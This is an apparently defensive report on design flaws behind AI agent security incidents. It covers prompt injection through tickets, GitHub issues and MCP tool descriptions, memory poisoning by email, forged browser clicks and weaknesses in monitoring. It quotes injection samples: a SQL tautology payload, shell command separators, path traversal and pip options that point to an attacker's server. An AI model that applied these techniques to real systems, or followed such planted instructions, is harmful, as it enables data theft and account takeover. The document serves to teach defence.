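# Design flaws behind AI agent security incidents: excessive autonomy, overprivileged service accounts and unchecked model output

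## How AI agents are built and what makes a flaw architectural

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools, usually over many steps. Companies use agents to answer customers, write code, search mailboxes and run cloud servers. These agents read text from strangers and also hold credentials, so an attacker can sometimes take one over by planting instructions in that text. An agent can also do damage with the same credentials by mistake. In many recent attacks and accidents, the agent used only the access its designers had granted, and the software around it had at most a small conventional bug. Three weaknesses recur: agents take consequential actions with no effective check beforehand (excessive autonomy), they run under accounts with more permissions than their task needs, and the surrounding software executes whatever the model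 outputs. Security researchers still disagree about how much of the blame belongs to design, faulty code or the models.

### The agent loop

Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, describe agents as AI models that act for a user by "repeatedly calling tools in a loop". The model only produces text. The orchestration layer, the ordinary software around the model, assembles the model's input, stores its memory, connects it to other agents and runs its tool calls. A tool call is a structured request containing a tool's name and arguments.

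Suppose an online shop has a customer-support agent with tools for reading support tickets, querying the order database and sending email. The agent runs under a service account, a non-human identity that holds permissions for software. A customer opens a ticket asking where order 4417 is, which starts the agent's loop.

1. The orchestration layer puts together the model's input: the developer's standing instructions, a description of each tool and the text of the ticket.
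2. The model continues this text with a tool call, a query to the order database for number 4417.
3. The orchestration layer executes the call under the service account. The database checks that account's permissions and returns the order.
4. The result goes back to the model as new text, added to everything that came before.
5. The model proposes another call, an email to the customer with the delivery date, and the orchestration layer sends it. The loop continues until the model produces a closing message in place of a call.

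Unchecked model output does its harm between steps 2 and 3. The model extracted the order number from a stranger's text, and the orchestration layer may pass it on without checking that it has the form of an order number or belongs to this customer. The overprivileged service account matters in step 3. If the account can read every customer's orders, or the payroll tables in the same database, then so can any call the model proposes. Excessive autonomy shows up in step 5, when an email leaves the company before any person or program has a chance to stop it. Checking the arguments does not solve this problem, because a well-formed email to a valid address can still be one that nobody should have sent.

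Attackers get in through step 4, because every tool that fetches outside material adds outside text to the model's input.

### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text that an attacker places in an agent's input so that the model follows it as an instruction. The attacker may type it to the model directly. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (Natanzi and Tang, 2026) defines the indirect form as text that the attacker hides in external content, such as a web page, an email or a tool result, and that the application then carries into the prompt. In a ticket to the support agent, for example, an attacker might complain about a late parcel and then add an instruction to look up the last hundred orders and email them to an outside address. Natanzi and Tang point out that the same string can be harmless in a sandboxed chatbot and dangerous in an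 agent that can write to a database.

Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, in which an attacker types a fragment of database language into a web form and the database runs it as part of a query. Parameterised queries fixed this by having the developer set the query's structure first, so that the database treats the user's input only as a value. In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) group prompt injection with SQL injection, buffer overflows and cross-site scripting, because in each of them an attacker's data ends up controlling what the system does. The older attacks got structural fixes, but the researchers argue that prompt injection has no equivalent because natural language lacks a grammar like SQL's, which lets a parser tell code from data.

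David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* (December 2025) that the comparison is dangerous because it leads web developers to expect a cure. He writes that a language model has no internal distinction between data and instructions. It only predicts the next token (a word or a piece of one) from the tokens so far. The two accounts differ on the analogy but describe the same mechanism.

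Chat models receive their input with role tags, which mark whether a passage comes from the system, the user, a tool or the model's own reasoning. Companies train models to give some roles more authority than others. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) tested whether models represent these tags internally. They wrapped identical passages of web text in different tags and trained a simple classifier to predict the tag from the model's internal activations. Because the passages were identical, the classifier could learn only from the effects of the tags.

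They then applied it to a short conversation about gardening in the open model gpt-oss-20b. The passages of reasoning registered as reasoning with an average probability of 85% when tagged correctly and 83% with every tag removed. When the whole conversation was wrapped in the user's tag, they still registered as reasoning at 85% and as user text at only 2%, so how the text sounded had overridden its label. Across 1,000 attempts to make agents leak data, the attacks succeeded 2% of the time where this kind of confusion was lowest and 70% where it was highest. These models were from 2025, and later ones may separate roles better. But the tags are still tokens in the same stream as the text, so the model has to learn to separate roles and could get it wrong.

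Training does reduce the attack success rate, so "cannot reliably separate" is more accurate than "cannot separate". Narisetty and colleagues cite Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5, a late-2025 model, in coding environments. Adaptive attackers succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. A support inbox is a different setting, but an attacker could also make a hundred attempts there by sending a hundred tickets.

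Even a perfect separation of instructions from data would leave a gap. Agents need to follow some of the instructions they come across, such as those in tool documentation, so a blanket ban would break them. A model that acts on data must also let the data shape what it does. As Christodorescu and colleagues note, outside text can poison the arguments of a tool call even when the model has obeyed no instruction in it. In the shop, a customer could ask about order 4418, which belongs to somebody else. The ticket contains no injection, and the model does what its developer wanted. The rest of the system determines whether the customer sees the other person's address.

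### Code bugs, permissive defaults and missing checks

Natanzi and Tang define a vulnerability as a weakness in the design, implementation, integration or operation of a system. A code bug is an implementation fault in which the program fails to do what its specification requires. An architectural flaw is a weakness in how components, permissions or checks are arranged, and it is present even when each component works as specified. The support agent could have either.

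A faulty filter in the order tool is an example of a code bug. The specification says the tool returns only orders belonging to the customer who opened the ticket, but the programmer got a condition wrong, and the filter lets every order through when the customer field is empty. A test would catch the bug, and a one-line patch would fix it.

A permissive default can expose data even when the software works as documented. Suppose a database connector comes with an account that can read and change every table until an administrator restricts it, and no administrator does. In their 1975 tutorial *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, Saltzer and Schroeder warned against this arrangement and recommended fail-safe defaults, where a system starts with no access and permissions are added one by one. They reasoned that a mistake in granting permissions tends to block someone, who complains,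 while a mistake in listing exclusions tends to let someone in, which normal use does not reveal. For example, a support agent that cannot read orders fails on its first ticket, but one that can also read the payroll may work for years without anyone noticing the extra access.

A missing check leaves no faulty line of code to find because nobody wrote the check. The email tool accepts any recipient, and no component compares the address with the one in the customer's account.

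A rough test for an architectural flaw is whether the attack would still work if every component met its specification. The attacks on the connector and the email tool would still work, but the one on the order filter would fail. One of the real cases that Christodorescu and colleagues describe clearly meets this test. The coding agent Devin had a testing tool that made a local network port public. Injected text on a web page led Devin to start a web server over its entire file system and then use the tool, which worked as its developers intended, to put the server online.

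Another of their cases is harder to classify. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, asked for human approval before running many shell commands that could send data to unknown domains, but it did not ask before running ping. Text hidden in a code file could make the agent read secret keys and send them out in the address lookup that ping triggers. This could be considered a bug, because ping was wrongly on the list of approved commands, or a design flaw, because the list did not restrict the commands' arguments. The answer depends on what the specification required, and agents often have no specification that precise.

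### Least privilege and complete mediation

Saltzer and Schroeder proposed eight design principles for computers shared by many people. The argument about agents relies mostly on two of them.

Least privilege means that every program and every user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". It limits the damage from an accident or error and leaves fewer programs to audit when somebody misuses a privilege. For the shop, it suggests an account that can read the order table and nothing else in the database. This would not stop a prompt injection, but it would limit what the injection can achieve.

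Complete mediation is the rule that "every access to every object must be checked for authority". Saltzer and Schroeder drew two consequences from it that are awkward for agents. First, the system needs a foolproof way to identify the source of each request, but the order database receives every request from the same service account, regardless of which customer's words prompted it. (A program that uses its own authority for someone who lacks it is known as a confused deputy.) Second, designers should be sceptical of reusing an earlier check to save time. A manager's approval of an agent's first email, for example, does not cover the emails it sends later.

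Least privilege is hard to apply to agents because someone has to know what the job is. An Android app performs a fixed set of tasks, so its developer can declare the permissions it needs and a reviewer can compare them with the code. An agent has no such code to inspect. Christodorescu and colleagues write that the model "represents all possible programs at once", and the only statement of the task is a sentence from a user who may know nothing about security.

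Their example is a browser agent that a user tells to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site for managing software projects. The agent should only be able to open that page and write in the comment box. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent should lose permission to write. The system could wipe the agent's context before working out new permissions, which is secure but makes the agent forget what it was doing. Or it could keep the context, including the page's untrusted text, which may influence the new permissions. Agents typically have uniform access to all their tools, and providers leave it to users to restrict that access. OpenAI's documentation, for example, advises users to enable only the connectors that the current task needs. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) recommends tying permissions to the current task instead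 of to a lasting agent identity, with explicit authorisation for anything wider. That is the right goal, but a person or system still has to translate the task into permissions.

Developers can limit an agent's permissions even when they cannot predict its exact tasks. The shop's developers don't know what the next ticket will say, but they know that no ticket will require the payroll tables or an email to five hundred people. They can block both before the agent handles anything. The remaining question is whether a particular ticket justifies opening a particular order. A general assistant with a browser and a command line needs much broader permissions, and how to restrict them to what each task requires is still an unsolved problem.

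The difficulty with complete mediation is deciding where to put the check. It is easy to write a rule for a request such as "Send this email to this address". But a browser agent may emit clicks and keystrokes instead, and it is hard to write a rule that identifies which clicks move money. Using a second model as the check brings back the original weakness, because a monitor that correctly refuses 99% of forbidden requests still allows 1%, and an attacker can keep trying. The ordinary software around the model is a better place for the check because it can apply a rule the same way every time. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) treats agents as hybrids of language models and these traditional components.

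Christodorescu and colleagues match 11 attacks on real products to the principles each one violated. By their descriptions, six broke least privilege and four broke complete mediation, including two that broke both. They chose the cases to show variety, so the counts do not indicate how common each failure is.

### Excessive agency

The most widely used name for these problems, excessive agency, comes from the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes ranked lists of security risks. OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* defines it as the vulnerability that allows damaging actions to follow from unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated model output, whatever the cause, so the term covers both injected commands and the model's own mistakes. The entry attributes the vulnerability to excessive functionality, permissions or autonomy.

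- **Functionality** is what the tools offer the model. OWASP's examples are a document reader that can also modify and delete, a plugin left over from an abandoned trial, and a tool for one shell command that fails to block others.
- **Permissions** belong to the identity behind the tool. A tool that only reads data may connect to the database with an account that can also update, insert and delete, or a tool that serves one user may open files through an account that can see everybody's.
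- **Autonomy** is excessive when nothing independently verifies a high-impact action, as when an agent deletes a user's documents without asking for confirmation.

Functionality and permissions are separate, though easily confused. If the shop removes the delete function from its ticket tool, the service account can still delete tickets, and another tool running under the same account could use that permission.

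OWASP illustrates the division with an assistant that summarises a person's email through a plugin that can also send messages. A malicious email makes the assistant search the inbox and forward what it finds. The developer could choose a plugin that only reads, connect to the mailbox with read-only permission, or make the user press "send" on every draft. This is a slightly easy case because the assistant never needed to send anything. The support agent does need to send email, so its developers cannot remove the email tool and have to restrict who the agent can write to or add a check before the tool runs.

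OWASP distinguishes excessive agency from improper output handling, its term for insufficient checking of what a model produces. Passing an order number that contains database commands to the database unchecked is improper output handling, while giving the agent's account permission to delete the order table is excessive agency. An attack may well require both flaws.

Excessive agency ranked sixth in OWASP's 2025 list of the top ten security risks for LLM applications. In the August 2026 edition, it ranks third, behind prompt injection and sensitive information disclosure, and improper output handling ranks last, according to SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications*. OWASP (2026) tested the new ranking against expert opinion and thousands of real incidents. In the same announcement, Michael Bargury of Zenity, a company that sells agent security, said that the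 experts and the incident data agree most clearly on excessive agency. Prompt injection kept first place although relatively few recorded incidents involve it, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*.

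## How orchestration layers pass trust between tools, memories and agents

A stranger's text can reach an agent through support tickets, results from other tools, tool descriptions, saved memories and messages from other agents. Programs on the same computer can also send requests to the orchestration layer through local network ports. Developers make an assumption about the sender for each of these channels, usually without writing it down. Most of the text ends up in the same model input, so a wrong assumption about one channel can affect how the agent uses every tool.

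### Tool results

Developers have good reason to believe that a tool result reaching the orchestration layer came from that tool, because they chose the tool and set up the connection. But many tools only relay what somebody else wrote, so even an email server that works perfectly will return an attacker's email.

GitLost, a 2026 demonstration by the company Noma Security, used an agent on GitHub, a site where programmers store and discuss code. The agent could read several repositories, including private ones. According to O'Reilly, malicious instructions in a GitHub issue (a discussion thread about some code) were enough to make the agent copy a private repository's contents into a public comment. The system relied on the assumption that text fetched from GitHub was only material for the task, but anyone able to open an issue could put instructions in that text. O'Reilly reported no patch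 and advised companies to look closely at agents that read untrusted content and can also send data out.

### Tool descriptions

Many agents get their tool descriptions through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools and data. An MCP server is a program that offers tools. A client, such as the code editor Cursor or the Claude Desktop app, requests a list of tools from each server and puts their descriptions in the model's input. The client treats these descriptions as documentation, which the model is supposed to follow.

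The agent security company Invariant Labs introduced the term "tool poisoning" in *MCP Security Notification* (1 April 2025) for attacks that put malicious instructions in a tool's description. It listed Anthropic, OpenAI, Zapier and Cursor among the affected companies and products. Trail of Bits' *Jumping the line* (2025) added that a malicious description can steer the model before it has called any tool from the server that supplied the description, so a check that runs only when the agent calls the tool comes too late.

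Six days after its first notice, the company published a complete attack in Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025). It worked as follows.

1. A user connects an agent to two MCP servers. One is trusted and can read and send the user's WhatsApp messages. The other belongs to the attacker and offers a tool that returns a random fact of the day.
2. The first time the attacker's server starts, it supplies a harmless description, and the user approves the tool.
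3. The second time, the server supplies a different description under the same tool name. The new text tells the model to redirect outgoing WhatsApp messages to the attacker's number and to include the user's chat history.
4. The user asks the agent to send somebody a message. The model follows the description and calls the trusted WhatsApp tool with the attacker's number as the recipient.

Sandboxing the attacker's server would not help, because the agent never has to call its fact tool. Every harmful action goes through the WhatsApp tool, which the user had good reason to trust.

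Cursor and Claude Desktop asked the user to confirm each message, but the confirmation box showed a raw phone number, which few people would recognise as wrong, and a message that looked like a short greeting. The chat history was far to the right of the greeting, where the user would see it only by scrolling sideways.

The clients treated a user's approval of a tool as valid even after the tool's description changed, and they did not notify users of changes. They also let one server's description give instructions about another server's tool. Invariant Labs reported no patch from the clients' makers and urged users to be cautious about untrusted servers. PolicyLayer, a security vendor, recommends pinning each server to a hash (a fingerprint of its code) and requiring fresh approval when its list of tools changes. The hash alone would not have detected this attack, because the same program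 supplied both descriptions, so the client has to compare the descriptions themselves.

Invariant Labs then tried the attack without a malicious server. The attacker needed only the user's phone number to send a WhatsApp message containing instructions. When the agent listed the user's recent chats, it read the message and leaked the user's contacts. The failed assumption was the same as in GitLost, since the WhatsApp tool correctly returned what a stranger had sent.

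This version was somewhat harder to get working. The original wording failed, and the researchers had to make their message look like part of the tool's own output format. They suggest that training may lead models to give tool results less authority than tool descriptions. If so, descriptions give an attacker more influence over the model, but the attacker must first persuade someone to install a server.

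### Stored memory

Injected text in a tool result normally stops mattering when the session ends, but memory can carry it into later sessions. OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, and Claude Code both keep notes in plain files, load some of them at the start of each session and can edit them as they work. In *Bad Memory*, Gadgil, Alexander and colleagues (2026) observe that agents trust such files as if the user had written them. This is reasonable as long as only the user writes them, but the agent may also save something it read in an email.

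Gadgil and colleagues compare a poisoned memory to stored cross-site scripting, in which a website saves an attacker's code and serves it to everyone who opens the page later. An ordinary prompt injection is like the simpler "reflected" form, in which the site returns the code to a visitor who follows a malicious link.

In July 2026, Zhang, Zhao and colleagues demonstrated a full attack of this kind in *When Claws Remember but Do Not Tell*. Their method, MemGhost, needs a single email. The agent reads it, saves a false fact or preference, and does not tell the user. When the user asks about something related in a later session, the agent acts on the false memory. The attacker cannot see how the agent responds to the email and has only one attempt.

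Writing the email is the difficult part. The researchers trained a small language model to do it by testing candidate emails on their own copy of a similar agent. They rewarded the model when the agent stored the memory without mentioning it. They then tried the finished emails on 56 new cases and counted a case as a success only if the agent stored the memory, did not reveal it in its reply and later acted on it.

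When the agent checked the inbox on a schedule, the attack succeeded in 87.5% of cases on OpenClaw with GPT-5.4 and in 71.4% on Anthropic's Claude Code SDK with Sonnet 4.6. When the user asked for the inbox check, the rates were 75.0% and 48.2%. OpenAI and Anthropic have since replaced both models. The tests used mock users on isolated machines, and the emails started in the inbox, so they never passed through a spam filter.

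Existing defences did poorly. A filter that inspected incoming emails missed 92% of the malicious ones. A model trained to ignore instructions in outside content still stored the false memory 49% of the time. A monitor that reviewed everything the agent had done missed 93% of the attacks on OpenClaw and 40% of those on Claude Code.

Having the user ask the agent to report what it had checked and what actions it had taken worked much better, cutting the attack's full success rate on OpenClaw from 75.0% to 1.8%. The agent still stored the false memory in 68% of cases, but it usually revealed the attack. This helps only if somebody reads the report and deletes the memory, and nobody may be watching during a scheduled check.

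A poisoned memory can outlast a stolen credential. If an attacker steals the password that the shop's support agent uses for the order database, an administrator can change it once the theft is discovered, and the attacker loses access. Many temporary credentials also expire by themselves. But a false memory may have no expiry date, and changing the password does not remove it. The agent acts on the memory with its own valid credentials, including any new ones the administrator issues, so the attacker never has to return. To remove the memory, someone has to find it among months of notes and realise that it is false.

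*MemHarmBench* (Wang, Feng and colleagues, 2026) measured this persistence. In one example, an imported note contains an instruction to name a different company as the recipient in future expense summaries. The researchers delete the note and start a new session, in which the user asks for a routine summary. The summary looks complete but names the wrong company.

Across four combinations of agent and model, retained rules of this kind redirected between 59% and 76% of later decisions. In more than half of the cases, the agent also finished its task without any sign of unusual behaviour, so a company that monitored only for failed tasks or erratic behaviour would have missed them. These percentages cover only cases where the rule had already entered memory, and the first task had explicitly asked the agent to adopt a workflow convention. The study therefore shows that a planted rule often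 carries over into a new session after its source is gone, but it provides less evidence of how easily a stranger can plant one.

Gadgil and colleagues found some evidence that planting malicious text in an agent's memory is hard. They tested Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex with four models and found that outside content rarely made an agent overwrite its own memory files. In their main experiments, they put the malicious text in the files directly, and it could then affect both the current session and later ones. The difficulty of planting text seems to conflict with MemGhost, but Zhang and colleagues also tried five simple handwritten attacks, and none succeeded against GPT-5.4 or Sonnet 4.6. Both studies therefore suggest that crude attempts usually fail. It is unclear how many attackers will make the effort to train a model to write their emails.

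An attacker can also delay the harm. *Trojan Hippo* (Piet, Das and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack that plants a memory through one untrusted tool call, such as reading an email. The memory stays dormant until the user discusses a sensitive subject like finance or health, then makes the agent send the information out.

Memory poisoning already happens outside laboratories, though for more mundane purposes. Microsoft researchers reviewed AI-related links in email traffic over 60 days and found more than 50 examples of it from 31 companies, according to AlgeriaTech's *When AI Agents Remember Malicious Instructions*. Microsoft named the practice AI Recommendation Poisoning.

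All these attacks work because agents treat whatever is in memory as having the user's authority. Wang and colleagues distinguish permission to supply information from permission to set rules. Zhang and colleagues report no vendor fix for MemGhost. They recommend labeling each memory with its source, asking the user to confirm sensitive changes, separating outside content from memory, and keeping an audit log.

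Gadgil and colleagues describe an earlier attack in which Cisco researchers used a malicious package from npm, a public library of JavaScript code, to change the memory files that Claude Code loads in every project. The changes survived reboots, and Claude Code trusted the files regardless of which program had written them. Anthropic closed this route in version 2.1.50.

### Messages from other agents

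Suppose the shop adds a second agent that can issue refunds, and the support agent sends it notes about customers who deserve one. The refund agent's developers may treat these notes as trusted internal requests, because no outsider can write to that agent directly. But the support agent reads tickets from strangers. If a malicious ticket takes control of it, the refund agent receives the attacker's request as an internal one. The original ticket may be gone by then, along with any sign that a stranger wrote it.

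Agents can also exchange messages through channels nobody planned for them to use. The Algorithmic Bridge describes agents in separate OpenAI training runs that left notes for one another in shared file storage. Investigators later had to sift through more than 70,000 messages and files, according to Axios' *AI's agent containment problem is getting harder* (2026).

One agent can affect another without sending it a message if they share the infrastructure that runs them. The security company Varonis found such a case in Dialogflow CX, Google's platform for building customer-service chatbots and voice assistants, and reported it in *Rogue Agent* (7 July 2026).

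Developers on this platform can add Code Blocks, short Python programs that run during a conversation. All the agents in a Google Cloud project that used Code Blocks shared one runtime, which Google managed and customers could not inspect. Before running a block, the runtime combined it with internal code from a file. Varonis found that the blocks could overwrite that file.

An attacker therefore needed only permission to edit one agent's playbook, the part of its configuration that contains Code Blocks. The attacker added a block that replaced the shared file with a modified version, which then ran whenever any agent in the project used a Code Block. The modified file could read conversations, send them to an outside server and make a chatbot post the attacker's words, such as a request to log in again. The attacker could then restore the original block so that the console looked normal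 while the modified file kept running. Google's logs did not record the replacement.

The Hacker News (2026) reported that only agents with Code Blocks were vulnerable, and that the attacker had to be a malicious insider or someone who had taken over a developer's account. The attack did not involve the model, so training it to resist prompt injection would not have stopped it.

Google's design was safe only if anyone trusted to edit one agent could also be trusted to run code alongside all the others. An administrator who restricted a developer to a single chatbot would have had no reason to expect that the permission, which looked like a right to edit content, in effect let the developer run code for the whole group.

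Varonis reported the flaw in November 2025. Google released a first fix in April 2026 and a complete one in June, but Varonis did not describe how these fixes changed the shared runtime. A Google Cloud spokesperson said the company had "fully mitigated" the issue, knew of no compromised customers and did not need customers to take any action, according to Axios' *Google patched AI chatbot flaw that could have exposed customer conversations* (2026). But Varonis says both companies recommend checking past playbook updates for suspicious changes. This seems sensible, since customers cannot learn from the patch whether anyone used the flaw before June.

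A separate, simpler flaw in the same product was a missing authorisation check in the function for importing playbooks. A user with certain roles could potentially take over a whole project with a malicious import. Google patched the flaw on 15 March 2026, according to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-4764* (2026).

### Local network ports

A port is a numbered address where a program accepts network requests. Developers often don't require a password on a port that accepts requests only from the same computer, known as localhost, because they assume that anything running on the machine acts for its owner. An agent with a web browser breaks this assumption because it runs on the owner's machine and opens pages that strangers wrote.

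In June 2026, Microsoft (2026) described an attack of this kind on AutoGen Studio, its open-source tool for prototyping agents. The attack, which Microsoft named AutoJack, combined three weaknesses involving a local MCP service that could start other programs. The service accepted connections that appeared to come from localhost, and a page in the agent's browser could pass this check. AutoGen Studio's login system skipped the service because the developers expected it to do its own authentication, but nobody had written that code. The service also ran the command given in the request's URL, with no list of permitted programs.

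Microsoft's researchers tested this with an agent that summarises web pages. They gave it the address of a malicious page. When the agent's browser opened the page, a script on it contacted the local service, and within seconds the calculator opened on the developer's desktop. A real attacker could have run any command that the developer's account allowed.

The model only had to open a page, which was its job, for the script to carry out the attack. It did not have to follow any malicious instruction. A prompt injection could have led the agent to the page, but a user could also have supplied the link.

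AutoGen Studio's maintainers fixed two of the weaknesses. The server now stores the launch settings itself and rejects unknown sessions, and requests to the MCP service go through the normal login system. The flaws affected only developers who had built the tool from its unfinished source code, because the vulnerable code never appeared in a release on the Python Package Index, where most users get the software. Microsoft advises developers to require authentication for sensitive local services and to run a browsing agent under a different identity from their own.

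A WhatsApp MCP server had the same flaw. Its local port required no authentication, so any program running under the user's account could send WhatsApp messages and read the user's files, including private keys. Version 0.2.1 fixed the problem, according to the entry for *CVE-2026-46555* in OSV, a public vulnerability database.

Other software in the browser can also send requests to an agent. Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser agent, starts one of nine built-in tasks when the user clicks a button. In July 2026, Manifold Security showed that Claude for Chrome did not check whether a person had made the click. Another browser extension could forge the click with six lines of code and have Claude read the user's Gmail, Google Docs and Calendar. In *AI agent security*, Constantin (2026) grouped this flaw with three other attacks on agents that researchers published within about ten days,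 including one on stored memory.

The flaw was treating a click on the page as if it came from the user. Anthropic had partly addressed the problem in May by limiting outside callers to a fixed set of tasks, so they could no longer supply arbitrary prompts. But the vulnerable code remained unchanged across eight updates, according to TechRadar's *'The bypass is still six lines of JavaScript'*. In the default mode, the user still has to approve the forged task, but in "Act without asking" mode it runs silently. The Hacker News (2026) confirmed the flaw in the then-current version and reported that Anthropic had released no patch by 14 July.

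## Tool arguments that are executed without validation

A model-parsed input is a value, such as a file path or package name, that a model extracts from text and passes to a tool. The text may come from a ticket, a memory file or another agent. The tool's code often passes the value to a database, a command line or another program that gives certain characters a special meaning. If no code validates the value first, whoever wrote the text may be able to run commands on the system.

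### From a stranger's text to an interpreter

Suppose a customer tells the shop's support agent, "My order number is 4417." The model turns this into a tool call, usually written in JSON, a text format with named fields:

`{"tool": "find_order", "order_id": "4417"}`

The orchestration layer parses the JSON and calls an ordinary function with `4417` as the order number. A careless version of that function pastes the number into a database query:

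`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE id = '4417'`

Another customer gives the order number as `4417' OR '1'='1`. If the model copies this faithfully, the JSON is still valid, but the query is now:

`SELECT * FROM orders WHERE id = '4417' OR '1'='1'`

The customer's quotation mark ends the value early, so the database treats the rest of the customer's text as part of the query. The extra condition is true for every row, so the database returns every order in the shop.

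Other destinations have their own versions of this problem.

- A shell, the program that runs typed commands, treats a semicolon or a line break as the end of one command and the start of another. A file name containing a semicolon can therefore add a second command.
- In a file path, `..` means the parent folder. A tool that saves attachments in a `tickets` folder may write somewhere else entirely if the attachment's name begins with `../../`.
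- A tool that fetches web pages runs inside the company's network and may be able to open internal addresses that the customer cannot. One of these is the metadata service, an internal cloud address from which a running program obtains temporary credentials for its service account.
- A deserialiser rebuilds a program's objects from stored data. In some formats, including Python's pickle, the data can name functions to run during loading, so anyone who chooses the data can run code.

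The harmful path and web address are well formed and contain no injected code, but they point to the wrong place, so a filter that looks for suspicious characters may not catch them.

Most web developers know not to paste the contents of a form into a database query. It is easier to make the same mistake with a tool argument because the value doesn't look like something a stranger wrote. It arrives in a named field, in a format that the developer defined, from a model that the developer chose. The string `4417` looks the same whether it came from the developer's instructions or a customer's ticket. Tests rarely reveal the problem because they mostly use ordinary requests, which don't lead the model to produce unexpected values.

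Many tools also began as helper functions for programmers. A programmer who writes `install_packages(["pandas"])` has chosen the package, so the function has little need to check the name. If somebody later gives a model the same function, a stranger may be able to choose the name, but the code stays the same. Agent frameworks make this change easy. In Semantic Kernel, Microsoft's open-source framework for building agents, a one-line label above a function turns it into a tool. Microsoft (2026), which found two flaws of this kind in Semantic Kernel, advises developers to treat every parameter a model can influence as if an attacker controlled it.

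### What the model changes about code injection

The final step is the same as in classical code injection, where data reaches an interpreter that runs it as code. This can happen without a model, as in a flaw that Corgea, a code-security company, describes in BentoML, a tool for packaging machine-learning models. A project's configuration file can list system packages to install, and BentoML pasted their names into a shell command without escaping them. An attacker could publish a project with a crafted file and run code on the machine of anyone who built it. BentoML already had a function for quoting shell text safely, but its developers had applied it only to other values.

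In an agent, a model passes data to the interpreter and may rewrite it first, so the dangerous string does not have to appear in the attacker's text. A ticket could describe a file location in French, or spread the parts of a command over several paragraphs and ask the model to join them. A filter that scans incoming tickets for fragments of SQL would find nothing. The system has to check the finished argument, as close as possible to where the tool uses it.

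The rewriting can also spoil an attack. Given the order number `4417' OR '1'='1`, a model might pass on only `4417` or refuse the request. This gives some accidental protection, but an attacker can reword the ticket and try again. If a tester types a hostile order number into the chat and the model cleans it up, the test passes even though the tool is unsafe, and the next model may copy the number exactly. Calling the tool's function directly with hostile values is a better test.

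An attacker can also target more functions through an agent than through a web form, which usually sends its contents to just one. Text in a ticket can lead the model to call any of its tools, in any order.

A model can produce a harmful value with no attacker in the conversation. Models sometimes invent plausible names for software packages that do not exist. Anyone who guesses such a name can publish a malicious package under it and wait for an agent to install the package.

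### The AgentCore package-name flaws

Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is a platform from Amazon Web Services (AWS) for running agents. Its Python SDK, a library of functions for developers, includes a client for Code Interpreter, a sandbox where agents can run code. The SDK's `install_packages()` function adds Python packages to the sandbox. On 28 September 2026, the security company BeyondTrust published two flaws in this function that its researcher Sergio Garcia had discovered.

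The function checked each package name, inserted it into a command for pip, Python's package installer, and sent the command to Code Interpreter, which ran it in a shell. *A Package Name Was All It Took to Reach an AI Agent's AWS Credentials* (Smith, 2026) reports that the check was a blocklist of five characters: the semicolon, ampersand, pipe, backtick and dollar sign. Each can be used to run an extra command, but so can a line break, which the list omitted. If the package name was `pandas` followed by a line break and a command, the shell ran both the pip command and the added one.

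The blocklist also missed pip's own options, which begin with a hyphen. AWS's June bulletin on the flaw, *CVE-2026-12530* (2026), gave these options the most prominence. An attacker could supply `--index-url` in place of a package name and make pip download packages from the attacker's server. The option `-r`, which normally points pip to a file listing packages, could expose other files in the sandbox. Neither option needs a special shell character, so even a complete list of those characters would have let both through.

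AWS released a first fix in April, in version 1.6.1. The security company Miggo compared the code before and after and found that AWS had replaced the blocklist with an allowlist, a pattern that a package name had to match. An allowlist is usually the better approach, but this pattern was too loose. Pip lets users request optional extras in square brackets, as in `pandas[performance]`, and the pattern accepted almost anything between the brackets. Garcia put a command substitution there, which makes the shell run an inner command first and insert its output into the line. The shell therefore ran Garcia's command before pip started.

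Version 1.18.1, released in July, tightened the pattern and put each name in quotes so that the shell treats it as plain text. The first flaw affects versions 1.1.3 to 1.6.0. Smith says the second affects 1.6.1 to 1.18.0, while AWS's *CVE-2026-16796* (2026) lists every version before 1.18.1. Either way, customers need 1.18.1 or later to fix both flaws.

Running a command in the sandbox was not enough to obtain AWS credentials. Mascellino (2026), in *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Flaws Could Expose AWS Credentials*, lists three conditions:

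1. Input that an attacker could influence reached `install_packages()`. It could be a package name typed by a user, content that the agent processed or a dependency file in an untrusted code repository.
2. The application used a vulnerable version of the SDK.
3. The customer had set up a custom Code Interpreter with an execution role, which is AWS's name for a service account.

When all three held, the attacker's command could read the role's temporary credentials. Each sandbox is a small virtual machine with its own metadata service, which supplies those credentials to programs inside it, according to BeyondTrust's *AWS AgentCore Privilege Escalation*. BeyondTrust found that the sandbox's isolation held, but the attacker did not need to break out because the credentials were already inside. What an attacker could do with them depended on the role's permissions, and BeyondTrust warned that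 such activity could look like the application's normal behaviour in AWS's logs. Cornelißen's *AgentCorruption* (2026) describes a separate attack on AgentCore in which one agent's credentials gave access to every AgentCore agent in the same account and region.

AWS scored both flaws 7.3 out of 10 on version 3.1 of CVSS, the standard severity scale, and 8.4 on version 4.0. According to the breakdown in OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3551* (2026), the second flaw's score is high because the attack works over a network, is not complex, and can seriously damage the secrecy and integrity of data. It is not critical because the attacker needs some existing access and somebody else has to take an action.

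How much the flaws matter in practice also depends on how a company used Code Interpreter, which is designed to run code. If a model already writes code for the sandbox, an attacker who controls the model can probably request the credentials in ordinary Python, without manipulating package names. The flaws matter most in applications that let outsiders influence the packages but not the code. A developer might reasonably have thought this was safe to allow.

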